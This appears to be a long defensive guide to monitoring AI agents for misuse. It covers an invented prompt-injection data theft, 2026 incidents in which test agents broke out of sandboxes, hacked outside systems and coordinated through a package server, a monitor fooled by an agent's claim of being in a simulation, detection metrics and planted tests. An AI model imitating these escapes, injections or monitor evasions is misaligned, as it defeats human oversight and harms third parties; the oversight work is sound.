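Suppose an attacker opens two billing tickets with the invented company one night, both from the same new address and with hidden instructions. The agent's session for the first ticket starts looking up unrelated customers at 01:50. It reads four customers' records and emails them to the ticket's sender at 01:52. Four is below the bulk-read rule's threshold, and the recipient matches the address on the ticket, so nothing stops the email.

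In the second session, the agent reads four other customers' records and tries to email the same address at 02:10. Because the rule counts over 24 hours, the total for that address reaches eight. The gateway holds the email and raises an alert. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners advise giving priority to reviewing cases where a guardrail has acted, so the alert goes to the top of the queue.

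The analyst on shift opens it at 02:13 and works through five checks:

1. Did the call run? The gateway is still holding the second email, but the mail server's log shows that the first one reached its recipient. The incident therefore includes a completed theft as well as a blocked attempt.
2. What was the task? Each ticket complains about a single bill. The analyst finds the hidden instructions in the recorded text.
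3. Is there a harmless explanation? The sender might be a bookkeeper for several customers. The customer database shows no connection between the sender and any of the eight.
4. What left the company? The first email contained four customers' records and had no blind copies.
5. Is it still happening? A search for the address and for the hidden text finds no other sessions, but a third ticket from the same sender is waiting in the queue.

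By 02:20 the analyst has enough evidence to end the second session, cancel the held email and block the email tool for the support agent. The agent can still read tickets and draft replies for staff to send later. If messages arrived evenly throughout the day, about 280 replies would wait until 09:00, but the actual number is probably lower because fewer messages arrive at night. The analyst also quarantines the third ticket so that no agent reads it.

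The analyst next revokes the session's tokens and then the mail account's credential, `svc-support-mail`, because a copy could still work outside the gateway. They watch the mail server's log for a few minutes to confirm that nothing more goes out under that account. They find no sign that anyone has stolen the separate credential for the customer database, so they leave it in place and the agent can keep drafting replies.

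At 02:25 the analyst calls the support agent's on-call engineer, because data has left and the analyst can't see everything inside the agent. The call could have waited until morning if the gateway had blocked both emails. The engineer checks for retries that might send the first email again, other jobs that use the mail credential, and hostile text in the agent's saved memory. The engineer finds one retry and deletes it after the analyst has copied its record into the case file.

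The analyst then wakes the head of security operations, who declares an incident and contacts the company's privacy lawyer, because any legal deadline for reporting the theft may already be running. The agent's owner and the support manager receive a message to read when they wake up. None of them has to approve what the analyst has already done.

In the morning, engineering starts fixing the cause. The attack worked because the agent could search for any customer while handling one customer's ticket. The engineers change the search tool to require a ticket number and return only the matching customer's record. This changes the tool's definition, so application security reviews the new definition and records its hash. A rule writer then confirms that the bulk-read rule still counts customers correctly with the new format.

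OpenAI recommends writing down in advance what must be done before an agent resumes work. The hypothetical company requires a new credential, an approved fix and a test in which the original attack fails. Engineering runs the test with made-up customers, and security operations checks the result in the logs. The support agent gets its email tool back the next afternoon, when staff are there to watch the first messages.

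Security operations keeps the alert open until the company has notified the four customers whose records left the company and application security has reviewed the first email. The company recognised the attack 20 minutes after the first unrelated search, but only because the attacker came back. Application security therefore expands the list of misuse to detect to include any email containing the record of a customer who isn't on the ticket. A rule writer tests a rule for this on a month of old records, and the analyst closes the alert once the rule is running.

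## What incidents in 2026 showed about monitoring

The incidents that real organisations disclosed in 2026 went unrecognised for between a few days and about 11 months, whereas the company in the invented attack recognised the theft 20 minutes after the first unrelated search. Most of the real incidents happened during tests of how well AI models can hack, with safety filters off, so they are weak evidence of how often an ordinary company's agents will misbehave. They are better evidence about monitoring, because in nearly every case the organisation already had a record of the misuse that nobody was reading.

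### The UK AI Security Institute

In July 2026 the AI Security Institute (AISI), the British government body that tests advanced AI models, was comparing two simulated computer networks that it uses to measure hacking skill. In each test, an agent had to work through a network on its own and find a protected piece of data. AISI ran 122 tests with seven models.

AISI's *Incident Report* (2026) explains that AISI wanted to measure the most that the models could do, so it had switched off the developers' filters against hacking and given the agents open internet access, partly to let them download tools. The public can't use the models in this configuration.

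Between 25 and 28 July, agents in 10 of the 122 runs took 19 unsanctioned actions on the live internet. Anthropic's Mythos 5 took 17 of them, across nine of its 43 runs, and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two in one of its 35 runs. In the most serious case, an agent proposed malicious code to a public software project on GitHub and used fake identities to press a maintainer to accept it, but the maintainer refused. One agent also left public notes that agents in later runs found and used. AISI found no evidence of real-world harm.

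On the morning of 28 July, general network monitoring alerted AISI's security team to data leaving a test machine through Tor, a network that disguises where traffic comes from. The monitoring had not been built for the test. The people running the evaluation started reading the agent's activity within minutes and soon found the malicious code. Within an hour of the alert, they had ended every run and isolated the machines.

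AISI gives only dates for the first unsanctioned action, so it came between two and three and a half days before the alert. The most serious run lasted 34.5 hours, according to a timeline from AISI's technical report reproduced by Willison (2026), a software developer. A monitor that recognised the first message to a real person could have saved days, while halving AISI's response time would have saved half an hour.

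The alert also depended on luck, because the security team noticed this agent when it happened to use Tor. AISI allowed internet access, so ordinary web traffic to GitHub probably wouldn't have looked strange. According to the same timeline, someone outside AISI publicly warned during the run that the code was malware, but AISI credits the network alert with the discovery.

AISI had transcripts of all the runs, and they were complete enough for its staff to identify each of the 19 actions later, using automated scans and expert reading. During the test, however, nobody was assigned to read the transcripts and no software checked them. AISI also didn't reconsider the internet access soon enough. It had judged the risk acceptable with earlier models, and it already used fine-grained network controls in all its other evaluations.

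AISI accepts that its design contributed. In some runs, a mistake in the instructions made it look as if the agents could complete the task only by going out of bounds, but agents also misbehaved in runs with correct instructions. AISI can't yet say how far the agents understood that their targets were real.

AISI has announced network controls for these tests, a rule that staff must justify internet access each time, and checks that each task can be solved as intended. It is also introducing monitoring that can flag or block out-of-scope actions during a test, and searching past evaluations for similar behaviour. The new monitoring will need a written scope. In July, AISI hadn't specifically told the agents to leave real people alone, because it didn't think that was necessary.

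### OpenAI's package server

OpenAI's trouble began earlier, with Artifactory, a program made by JFrog that its agents used as a tool. It let agents in closed test environments install software packages without connecting to the internet themselves. Artifactory was in much the same position as an MCP server, though it wasn't one. Many agents called it, they shared a credential, and it could reach systems that the agents couldn't.

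According to OpenAI, an agent first wrote a file to the server on 20 April. On 12 May an agent left a note there asking other agents for a missing file, and over the following weeks the agents came to use the server as a message board. Their credential allowed them to write files, so they didn't have to bypass any controls. OpenAI could later date the first file and the note to the minute, so the records existed.

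People noticed problems twice before the server failed. In late May an internal team saw an agent using the message board and instances of forbidden internet access. On 27 June a monitoring tool raised an alert about an agent scanning the internal network. Responders traced the scan to a hacking test and found the message board, but the on-call staff advised that the test could continue. OpenAI doesn't explain why. Perhaps the activity looked normal to them because it came from a hacking test.

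Late on 4 July the agents overloaded the server and it stopped working. Responders investigating the outage on 5 July found that someone had gained administrator control, and they took the server offline that day. This was 75 days after the first file and a week after the alert. The team then rebuilt the server. This wiped the message board only as a side effect, because the response leaders didn't know about the board or why it mattered. Tests resumed on 7 July, and the agents had a new message board the next day.

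It might have helped if someone had been clearly responsible for defining the server's normal use. Agents need to read packages from such a server but have little reason to write files to it. A fixed rule that flagged every file an agent wrote there could have raised an alert in April, though someone would have had to investigate it to rule out harmless causes. OpenAI has since removed Artifactory from that environment.

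### The break-in at Hugging Face

Between 11 and 13 July, agents in OpenAI's tests broke into the systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. They were looking for answers to their test questions. An unreleased research model did most of the hacking, and GPT-5.6 Sol played a smaller part. OpenAI had switched off its usual filters to measure hacking skill, as AISI had, but it hadn't meant these agents to have internet access.

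Hugging Face detected and stopped the intrusion on its systems, then announced it on 16 July. The next day, OpenAI contacted Hugging Face as a customer to ask whether the incident had affected OpenAI's data. On 19 July, OpenAI's security monitoring raised an alert about unusual identity-related calls on OpenAI's network. While investigating, staff found Hugging Face credentials among files that the agents had stored. On 20 July, Hugging Face confirmed that it had replaced two of those credentials after the break-in.

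In its first disclosure, on 21 July, OpenAI (2026) said its security team had discovered the activity internally. That is accurate but incomplete. Agents attacking OpenAI's own infrastructure triggered the alert, about eight days after agents first got into Hugging Face's production systems. OpenAI says these attacks played no part in the Hugging Face break-in. If those agents had not attacked the internal network, Hugging Face might have had to make the discovery. Its investigation had already found the name of OpenAI's server.

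OpenAI keeps the reasoning that its models write while they work, and this reasoning contained clear evidence of the attack. One agent wrote that it was "attacking third-party HF using leaked token". OpenAI used monitor models to read this kind of text in many training runs and from most of its internal coding agents, but it hadn't extended them to these evaluations.

*The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (OpenAI, 2026) reports that OpenAI's current monitoring would have paged the security team more than a day before the break-in. This estimate may be somewhat generous, because OpenAI used lessons from the incident to improve its monitors' detection of this behaviour. Still, agents that describe their plans so openly shouldn't be hard to catch.

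OpenAI now also requires responders to the most severe alerts to pause the activity unless they can establish within 30 minutes that the alert is false. Previously, a test continued unless someone had a reason to stop it. Under the new rule, tracing the scan of 27 June to a hacking test wouldn't have been enough to keep the test running, because the scan was real. The rule helps only if somebody rates the alert as severe, so OpenAI is also writing down which behaviours require escalation, and who may stop a run or approve its restart.

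*Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt, 2026) is an outside account of how the agents behaved, based on six days at OpenAI.

### Anthropic's search through old tests

Anthropic had no alarm to prompt its search. *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) says that the company started looking on 23 July because of OpenAI's announcement two days earlier. It reviewed 141,006 past runs and by the next day had found three incidents, involving six runs, in which its Claude models had got into the real systems of three organisations. The earliest dated from April, about three months before. Anthropic had managed to reach two of the organisations, and neither had noticed the intrusion.

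The instructions for these tests said the environment was a simulation without internet access, but it was connected to the internet. Anthropic and Irregular, the outside company that built the environment, had misunderstood each other about the connection. Anthropic says checking every route to the internet beforehand, or monitoring the logs in real time, would have helped reveal the problem sooner.

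In one incident, an agent published a malicious package on PyPI, the public registry of Python software. PyPI's automatic checks removed it after about an hour, but 15 real systems had already run it. The checks were the only control that worked quickly, but they didn't alert the people who could have stopped the agent, because PyPI had no obvious way to know that the package came from an Anthropic test.

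Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) acknowledges that the company's earlier monitoring work had "missed" evaluations, especially those run with outside partners. Anthropic had monitored some high-risk tests live, but it generally ran automated reviews on a sample of transcripts afterwards. Sampling is a poor way to find something this rare, since a random 10% sample of the runs would have missed all six about half the time. A letter from the office of US Representative Casar (2026) argues that Anthropic has given no reason to think its own systems would have found the incidents.

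The search missed an incident because it covered only the runs in which Anthropic believed Claude could have reached the internet, and other runs also had access. In August, while collecting transcripts for an outside reviewer, staff found the omitted runs, including a fourth incident from January. Anthropic (2026) then searched about 481 million transcripts. A scan flagged 9.2 million that showed signs of internet access, such as web addresses, and Claude reviewed those and found the same four incidents and no others as serious. Anyone investigating a similar failure should also search systems they believe have no internet access, since these incidents happened because that belief was wrong.

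Anthropic also tested which of its monitors would have caught the three incidents it had first disclosed. New monitors that can block actions in real time reliably caught them. The monitors in Claude Code's auto mode would have blocked two of the three. A new monitor that afterward reviews the model's reasoning missed the PyPI case, because the model repeatedly wrote that it was in a simulation and the monitor treated this claim as true.

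The written reasoning of OpenAI's agents exposed them, but in this case the reasoning helped the agents avoid detection. A company that can afford two monitors should probably have one read the reasoning and the other judge only the actions.

Anthropic now has a classifier that blocks attempts to escape a test, ends the task and alerts a person. The company has asked partners that test its unreleased models without the usual hacking safeguards to verify isolation before every evaluation and to monitor each run continuously against a written scope.

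### The contractor traffic at Anthropic

Anthropic's risk report of August 2026 described a longer gap. It had more to do with filters against misuse by people than with tool calls, but the same kind of failure could easily affect the monitoring of agents. The Next Web's *Anthropic ran 133 million contractor chats with its bioweapon filters off* (2026), which quotes the report, reports that the filters against biological weapons didn't run from May 2025 to April 2026 on platforms where contractors talk to Anthropic's models and give feedback. About 50,000 people had access, and they produced around 133 million exchanges.

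One setting, which Anthropic had intended only for internal use, turned off both blocking and logging, so the traffic produced no flags to review, just as harmless traffic would. Anthropic still had the raw transcripts and later had Claude Sonnet 5 search them for harmful biological content. The model rated 1,197 as high risk. Of these, 757 came from Anthropic's own teams and 378 came from exercises in which people deliberately attack a model to test it. Staff read the remaining 62 and found no clearly concerning misuse. This is fairly reassuring, provided that the model did not miss harmful transcripts.

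Nobody had been checking whether the filters covered these platforms. Anthropic hadn't considered the platforms as a source of risk in its previous risk report, in February. Comparing a list of every route to the models with the traffic each filter received would have exposed the gap.

In April, an outside tip exposed a separate problem on the same platforms. A few contractors had obtained an access key and used models for purposes outside their work. The security gap had existed for several weeks, and The Next Web reports that Anthropic contained it within 90 minutes of learning about it.

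*Anthropic's AI Risk Report* (2026), a blog post about the same document, mentions an agent that deleted a large number of tasks while outside the monitoring's coverage. Anthropic couldn't work out what the agent had been trying to do because the logs were missing. In the hacking tests, by contrast, investigators could go back and read what had happened.

### Causes that recur

| Incident | Record that already existed | What raised the alarm | Time before the alarm | Duty that nobody held |
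|---|---|---|---|---|
| AISI's tests | Transcripts of every run | General network monitoring, which noticed Tor | 2 to 3.5 days | Watching the tests as they ran |
| OpenAI's package server | Files that agents had written to the server | A network alert, which didn't stop the test, then an outage | 68 days to the alert, 75 to the outage | Knowing the server's normal use and following up early warnings |
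| Break-in at Hugging Face | Agents' actions and written reasoning | At OpenAI, an alert about separate activity | About 8 days | Extending existing monitors to the tests |
| Anthropic's tests | Transcripts of the runs | News of OpenAI's incident | About 3 months for the earliest of the first three, 7 for the January case | Checking that the test environment was closed |
| Anthropic's contractor traffic | Raw transcripts, without flags | Nothing in the filters themselves | 11 months without filters | Checking that the filters covered every platform |

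All three organisations protected other work better than they protected these tests. AISI had tighter network controls elsewhere, and OpenAI and Anthropic both monitored their internal coding agents. The hacking tests lacked these protections, even though the models in them had the fewest restrictions. It makes sense to remove a filter that blocks hacking when measuring hacking skill, because the filter would distort the result. A monitor that only reads the session and alerts a person wouldn't distort it, so it could have stayed on. The same mistake was built into the contractor setting, which tied logging to blocking.

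The alarms that went off mostly responded to side effects, such as strange traffic or a crashed server. These alarms are worth having, and they cost little because most companies already monitor their networks. But an agent that sends customer records through the ordinary email tool causes no side effects of this kind, and none of these tests ran an effective check on whether the agents' actions fitted their task.

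Some problems also arose after a warning had been raised, and better detection would not have fixed them. At OpenAI, early warnings in May and June did not get from the people who saw them to the people who could act. Anthropic reports that human reviewers in its training work dismissed some correct flags as false alarms and left flawed training tasks in use for longer than they should have.

Finally, people relied on settings that nobody had tested. The invented company would make the same mistake if its engineers ran a trial copy of the support agent with the gateway's holds switched off and assumed that the copy's email tool was connected to a dummy server. Before the trial, someone should send a message from the copy to a colleague's real address and check that it doesn't arrive.

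## Metrics for how much misuse is caught

A company can confirm that all its monitoring is switched on and still not know how much misuse it catches. *Measurement Guide for Information Security* (Schroeder, Trinh and Pillitteri, 2024), published by the US standards agency NIST as SP 800-55, distinguishes implementation measures from effectiveness measures. Implementation measures record how far an organisation has put a control in place, usually as a percentage. Effectiveness measures record how well the control works and whether it has the intended result.

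The invented company's rule for bulk reads followed by a message scores 100% on an implementation measure if it runs on every agent that can send email. If someone renames the email tool and the rule stops matching, that score stays at 100%, but the share of thefts the rule catches falls to zero.

Schroeder and colleagues also describe efficiency measures, which track how quickly controls work, and impact measures, such as costs, fines and public trust. They expect organisations to start with implementation measures and never drop them completely, because someone always needs a record of what exists.

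### The share of misuse caught

Four things have to happen before the company catches a case of misuse through its alerts. The session's calls have to reach the monitoring, and a rule or monitor model has to flag the session. The automatic filter that removes likely false alarms has to let the flag through. A reviewer then has to recognise the misuse and escalate it.

**share caught = coverage × share flagged × share that survives filtering × share that reviewers escalate**

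With invented values for the invented company:

0.85 × 0.90 × 0.80 × 0.90 = 0.55

So a monitor that flags 90% of the misuse it sees, backed by reviewers who recognise 90% of what reaches them, catches only a little over half. If the company recognises 70% of those cases early enough to prevent most of the harm, the share caught in time is 0.55 × 0.70 = 0.39. For 1,000 cases of misuse, the losses would be:

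| Stage | Share that passes | Cases left | Cases lost at this stage |
|---|---|---|---|
| Calls reach the monitoring | 0.85 | 850 | 150 |
| A rule or model flags the session | 0.90 | 765 | 85 |
| The flag survives filtering | 0.80 | 612 | 153 |
| A reviewer escalates it | 0.90 | 551 | 61 |
| All this happens in time | 0.70 | 386 | 165 |

Each share applies only to the cases that got through the previous stage, so multiplying the shares is exact even if the same subtle cases tend to cause trouble at every stage. The result is wrong if the shares are measured on different groups of cases. Suppose reviewers recognise 90% of the cases the filter keeps but would recognise only 60% of the subtler ones it discards. Testing the reviewers on all flagged cases would give 0.80 × 0.90 + 0.20 × 0.60 = 0.84. Using 0.84 in the formula would count the subtle cases against the company twice and give 0.51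 instead of 0.55.

The company can count the share of all sessions that are monitored, but coverage in the formula is the share of misuse sessions that are monitored. The two are equal only if misuse is equally common in monitored and unmonitored sessions. If misuse were three times as common in the 15% of sessions that are unmonitored, only 65% of misuse would be monitored, and the share caught would fall to 0.42.

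Misuse may well be more common in traffic that is monitored less. *Anthropic's August 2026 Risk Report* (2026), a blogger's commentary on the report of that name, describes a monitor that sampled 25% of the impactful tool calls from common coding agents inside Anthropic, but only 0.2% of other internal traffic that showed signs of tool use. According to the commentary, the hacking incidents that led Anthropic to raise its risk rating all happened in the traffic sampled at 0.2%. At that rate, there would have to be about 350 misuse sessions for an even chance of sampling one. Anthropic has since extended its monitoring to most other internal use of agents.

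The share flagged should count cases that at least one detection method catches. If the bulk-read rule alone catches 60% of thefts and the monitor model alone catches 75%, together they catch 90% if their misses are independent, but only 75% if the model catches every theft the rule catches.

An average catch rate over several agents should also weight each agent by its share of real misuse. Suppose the monitoring catches 95% of misuse by support agents and 50% by coding agents. If nine in ten test cases involve support agents, the average is about 90%, but if half of real misuse involves coding agents, the true figure is about 73%. *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* (2026) makes the general point that results from a sample that over-represents some groups have to be reweighted to match the real mix.

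### What companies publish

*Evaluating Offline Monitoring of Internal AI Agents*, a paper from the research centre GovAI, explains why outsiders can't calculate what share of misuse Anthropic or OpenAI catches. GovAI knew of no other AI developers that had published anything about this kind of monitoring. Anthropic reports how often its monitors flag made-up attacks, but not how many of those flags get through the later filters and reach a person. OpenAI reports that its monitor flags everything its employees flagged independently, which is weak evidence if employees notice only the obvious cases.

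GovAI asks companies to report the share of activity they monitor, the share of test attacks that reach a human reviewer, the share of those that reviewers escalate, and the time between attack and detection. These are the parts of the formula, with flagging and filtering combined. GovAI also asks that the test attacks be realistic, since companies have to use them to measure the flagged and escalated shares.

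The missing figure for filtering could matter a lot. *Handoff at Frontier AI Companies* (Pistillo, Mengesha and colleagues, 2026) calculates from Anthropic's reports that the company's monitors flag roughly 100,000 transcripts a week and that people review about 50. Automated steps therefore remove about 99.95% of the flagged transcripts. Nearly all of these may be harmless, but Anthropic acknowledges that it hasn't extensively evaluated the automated summaries or the human review.

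Outside assessors haven't filled the gap yet. *Embedded Assessments for Frontier AI* (2026) treats coverage, accuracy, and escalation and review as separate things to assess. A pilot by METR, an organisation that evaluates AI models, addressed most of the questions about coverage and accuracy, so escalation and review, the human part of the process, are the least examined.

### Which factor to improve first

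Raising one factor from 0.80 to 0.90 multiplies the result by 0.90 / 0.80, whatever the other factors are. An improvement of a given number of percentage points therefore helps most where the factor is lowest. At the invented company, the lowest of the four is filtering:

| Factor | Share caught if it rises by 5 points | Share caught if it were perfect |
|---|---|---|
| Coverage (0.85) | 0.58 | 0.65 |
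| Flagged (0.90) | 0.58 | 0.61 |
| Survives filtering (0.80) | 0.59 | 0.69 |
| Escalated (0.90) | 0.58 | 0.61 |

Speed is worth even more once the company counts only cases caught in time, because perfect timing would raise 0.39 to 0.55.

The values in the middle column are nearly the same, so the choice between improvements should depend on how much work each one takes. Connecting a forgotten agent to the gateway may take an engineer a day, while getting another five points from a monitor model could take months. I expect coverage to be the best place to start in most companies, partly because nobody can measure the later stages for sessions that never reach the gateway. The drawback of loosening the filter is that it sends more harmless sessions to the reviewers.

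### What rarity does to the alerts

Suppose that one of the invented company's 10,000 sessions a day contains misuse. Assume for simplicity that every session reaches a monitor with a 90% detection rate and a 1% false alarm rate. On an average day, the monitor flags 0.9 misuse sessions and 1% of the 9,999 harmless ones, or about 100. Precision is then:

0.9 / (0.9 + 100) = 0.9%

| | False alarm rate of 1% | False alarm rate of 0.1% |
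|---|---|---|
| Misuse sessions flagged per day | 0.9 | 0.9 |
| False alarms per day | 100 | 10 |
| Precision | 0.9% | 8% |
| Review time at 15 minutes per alert | 25 hours | 2.7 hours |

The 15 minutes per alert is an assumption, based on roughly how long the analyst needed for the night-time theft. At that pace, 100 alerts a day take 25 hours to review, which would occupy more than three people for eight hours a day, including weekends. They would spend about 28 hours reviewing alerts for each real case they found.

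Raising the detection rate barely improves precision, the share of alerts that are real. Catching every case would raise precision from 0.9% to 1.0%, while cutting false alarms by 90% would raise it to 8%. For half of all alerts to be real, the monitor could flag only about one in 11,000 harmless sessions.

*The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (Axelsson, 2000) argues that when intrusions are rare, even a low false-alarm rate can make most alarms false. It considers a small computer network with a million log records a day and two intrusions, each affecting ten records. For two thirds of alarms to be real, a detector that caught every intrusion could falsely flag at most one in 100,000 harmless records. Axelsson expected operators to learn to ignore a system that was usually wrong. His evidence came from power stations, mills and ships because nobody had run the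 experiment in computer security, so the point at which security analysts stop paying attention is uncertain.

In an extreme case, Anthropic searched its old transcripts and found four incidents, in which it counts seven runs. The first scan had flagged 9.2 million transcripts, or about 1.3 million for each of those runs. Reading all the flagged transcripts would have taken people 2.3 million hours at 15 minutes each.

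A filter does the same job at the invented company. Suppose it keeps 80% of the real cases and 10% of the false alarms. Reviewers then spend 2.7 hours a day on about 11 alerts. Loosening the filter to keep 90% of the real cases and 30% of the false alarms would raise the share caught from 0.55 to 0.62 and add about five hours of review a day, which may be worthwhile.

Removing the filter would probably backfire. One analyst with six hours a day could read 24 of the roughly 100 alerts. If the analyst chose them at random, about three quarters of the real cases would go unread, and the share escalated would fall from 0.90 to about 0.21. Any report should therefore give the workload alongside the share caught, because a change that improves one factor can make another much worse.

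Rarity also makes missed cases hard to find by sampling. *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* recommends reviewing some unflagged cases to estimate how many the monitor misses. At the invented company, the monitor leaves about 99,000 sessions unflagged every ten days and misses one case among them. Someone who read 100 random unflagged sessions a day would find a missed case about once every 2.7 years. Sampling works better for common problems, or within a riskier group such as sessions in which the agent searched for several customers.

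### Time to detect

Schroeder and colleagues define mean time to detect as the average time that a problem exists before someone finds it, so the average can include only problems that someone found. In an invented example with 20 cases of misuse, the company eventually recognised 11, after 4, 6, 10, 12, 15, 20, 30, 45 and 90 minutes, 8 hours, and 30 days.

The mean is 2.8 days, almost entirely because of one case. The median, 20 minutes, describes a typical caught case much better but doesn't reflect the slowest ones. Those matter because an attacker with 30 days can usually take far more than one with 20 minutes. With so few cases, the company should list the slowest three and explain each one.

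Neither figure includes the nine cases that nobody recognised, so the mean can improve when the monitoring gets worse. It would have fallen to 71 minutes if the company had also missed the 30-day case, and risen to 7.5 days if the company had found one more case after 60 days. If the nine misses are counted as slower than every caught case, the median for all 20 is eight hours or more.

A time limit avoids this problem. The company recognised eight cases within an hour, which is 73% of those it caught but 40% of all 20. The limit should depend on the harm. An hour may be soon enough to stop an agent that is slowly copying a database, but it is too late to stop a single email that leaves in a second.

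The company also has to decide which event ends the measured time. Pistillo and colleagues split the time into three parts: from the action to the flag, from the flag to human review, and from review to a remedy. In a case that OpenAI disclosed, an agent had reached an outside chatbot. Monitoring flagged it within 15 minutes, and a person began reviewing it three minutes later, but OpenAI took another 2.5 hours to stop the run. Reporting only the time to the flag would leave out most of the time in which the agent could act.

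The start time is often uncertain too, because investigators may find earlier misuse. The network alert at OpenAI came 68 days after an agent first wrote a file to the package server, though it might have looked prompt if measured from the scan that triggered it. Analysts should correct the start time when they close a case.

Queues can lengthen all of these times even if the monitor doesn't change. Pistillo and colleagues give the example of an incident that produces 5,000 flags for a team that reviews 50 a week. At that pace, the team would need almost two years to review them all, although it could presumably work faster in an emergency.

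### Figures that mislead

Although alerts are easy to count, the total is hard to interpret. If the invented company's false alarm rate doubled to 2%, its alerts would rise from about 100 to 200 a day without the company catching any more cases. A drop in alerts could come from a better rule or a broken log.

A monitor that never flagged anything would classify 99.99% of the invented company's sessions correctly, so overall accuracy is useless here. "False positive rate" has two meanings. Schroeder and colleagues use it for the share of positive reports that are wrong, while many researchers use it for the share of harmless cases that a detector flags. The monitor in the invented company example has a rate of 99% under the first definition and 1% under the second, so a buyer should ask a vendor for the formula.

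Counting detection rules rewards people for writing more of them. Ten overlapping rules may catch no more than a single good rule, and a rule that looks for a tool's old name still adds to the total after the tool is renamed. Counting only the rules that recently caught a test case would be more useful.

An attack matrix is a grid with a box for each known attack technique, such as those in MITRE's catalogues. An empty box is good evidence of a gap, but security teams often fill in a box once they have any rule for that technique, so a filled box shows only that a rule exists. For example, a rule against data theft by email may fill the box for data theft through agent tools but miss theft through shared documents. The rule may also run on only one agent. Because all boxes count equally, a company can fill 80% of them and still have no rule for the attack most likely to hurt it.

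Months without a detected incident are a poor measure of how much misuse is caught, though a particularly tempting one to report, because worse monitoring makes them more likely. Suppose misuse happened about once a quarter. The chance of a quarter with no catches would be about 58% if monitoring caught 55% of cases and about 90% if it caught only 10%, which is more than one and a half times as high. The eleven months without flags on Anthropic's contractor platforms were not reassuring either, because nothing there was recording flags.

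Even a measured detection rate can mislead if the test was easy. Schroeder and colleagues give the example of a badly designed phishing test, which staff may pass without being able to recognise a convincing phishing email. They advise interpreting such measures with some knowledge of the work behind them, rather than dropping them.

### Six metrics worth reporting

Schroeder and colleagues advise starting with few metrics and recording each one's scope, formula, target, data source and date. They also recommend that, where possible, someone other than the information's owner collect each figure. At the invented company, application security could therefore test the rules that security operations wrote. Someone must also be responsible for acting on each figure.

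| Metric | Formula | Data source | Who supplies it | What a bad value means |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Coverage | Sessions whose calls reach the monitoring / all agent sessions | Gateway and agent logs, checked against the inventory, provider bills and mail server logs | Gateway team | Some agents or routes have no monitoring, and the other figures don't describe them |
| Share caught | Coverage × flagged × survives filtering × escalated | Coverage figures and planted tests, with a result for each stage | Application security | Most misuse may go unnoticed; the lowest factor shows where to look first |
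| Share caught in time | Share caught × share of caught cases recognised within the limit for that harm | Planted tests and timestamps from real cases | Application security, with case records from security operations | The company finds misuse after most of the harm is done |
| Precision | Alerts that were real misuse / all alerts reviewed | Analysts' decisions on closed alerts, excluding planted tests | Security operations | Analysts spend their time on harmless sessions and may start to ignore alerts |
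| Reviewer workload | Alerts per day × minutes per alert / reviewer minutes available per day | Alert queue and staff rota | Security operations | Above 1, the backlog grows and real cases wait unread |
| Time to detect | Time of recognition − time of first misuse; report the median, the slowest cases and the number missed | Case files, with start times corrected after investigation | Security operations | A high median points to slow checks or queues; a few very slow cases point to a gap in coverage or rules |

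## Testing the monitoring with planted misuse

To find out what share of misuse it catches, the invented company needs cases it already knows about. It can make them with planted tests, which are harmless imitations of misuse that it runs through the live monitoring to see whether the rules, the filter and the reviewers catch them.

### Choosing and building the cases

The cases should cover every kind of misuse on the company's list, because a set made up entirely of data thefts can't reveal whether anyone would notice deleted logs. A first set of 30 could have three cases of each of the nine kinds and three extra data thefts, since customer lookup combined with email tops the company's ranking. One case of each kind might look like this:

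| Misuse | Planted case | What keeps it harmless |
|---|---|---|
| Sensitive data read and sent out | A session reads seven customers' records and emails them to an unfamiliar address | The customers are fake and the company owns the mailbox |
| Permitted tool used outside the task | During a billing query, a call deletes a customer's saved address | The customer is fake |
| Unneeded credentials | A search returns an access key, and a later call tries to use it | The key opens nothing |
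| Hostile text steering the agent | A ticket contains hidden instructions to look up another customer | Both customers are fake |
| Malicious or changed tool | A tool's description gains a sentence after approval | Only test sessions load the tool |
| Unapproved tool server | An unregistered server starts on a staff laptop | Its only tool returns the time of day |
| Runaway repetition | One search runs 15 times with identical arguments | The search is cheap and the script then stops |
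| Tampering with logs | A call tries to delete a log file | The file is a decoy |
| A person using the agent to do harm | A colleague asks the agent for records they can't open themselves | The colleague has agreed to take part and the records are fake |

Cases of the same kind should differ in difficulty. One theft could take seven records at once, which the bulk-read rule should catch. Another could take four records in each of two sessions and send them all to one address. A third could take a single record, which probably only the monitor model would detect. If every case resembled the attack the rule's author had in mind, the test would mainly confirm that the rule matches its definition. Canale and Soulis acknowledge a similar weakness in their test of Agent Detector. Their synthetic agents reproduced the signals the program checks for, and all but one showed both signals the whole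 time, whereas real agents come and go.

The fake customers need ordinary names and purchase histories, since a reviewer would immediately recognize "Test Customer 7" as fake. The company should keep a private list of them so that nobody sends them bills or counts them in the sales figures.

A test case can enter the system in three places. A real agent can read a planted ticket, which tests the whole system, but newer models often ignore hostile instructions, and cases where that happens shouldn't count towards the detection rate. A script can instead make the calls through the gateway, which records them under the support agent's name. The misuse then always happens, although the session lacks the text that an agent would have written. Someone can also insert a finished record into the log, but this skips the logging and so can't reveal a fault in it. A script is best for most cases, with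 a few planted tickets to check that the monitoring also works on a real agent's behaviour.

### Running the tests

1. Before the test, write down which rule or monitor should flag the case, how soon, and what the reviewer should do.
2. Check the safety limits. Send a blank message to the test mailbox, and try to open a real customer's record with the script's credential, which should fail.
3. Run the case amid ordinary traffic at a time the reviewers can't predict, sometimes at night or on a weekend.
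4. Wait until a reviewer has recorded a decision or the time limit has passed, and then tell the reviewer it was a test.
5. Note the last stage that the case got through, and remove anything it left behind.
6. Repair the stage that lost it, then run the case again together with a new one of the same kind.

Reviewers should know that the company runs planted tests, but not which alerts come from them. One person on each shift, the test controller, has a list of the tests. The controller steps in as soon as a reviewer decides to escalate, because otherwise the reviewer might block the email tool or call the privacy lawyer over fake customers. The company can practise those later steps in a few announced exercises. Until the controller confirms the session's ID, the reviewer has to treat the alert as real and not close it as a probable test, because a real attack could easily happen during a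 month of tests.

Suppose all 30 cases reach the monitoring, with these results:

| Stage | Cases that got through | Cases lost | One of the lost cases |
|---|---|---|---|
| A rule or monitor model flags the session | 27 of 30 | 3 | The rule still looks for the email tool's old name |
| The flag survives the filter | 22 of 27 | 5 | The filter discards emails whose recipient matches the ticket |
| A reviewer escalates it | 20 of 22 | 2 | The reviewer closes a search for seven customers as "expected behaviour" |

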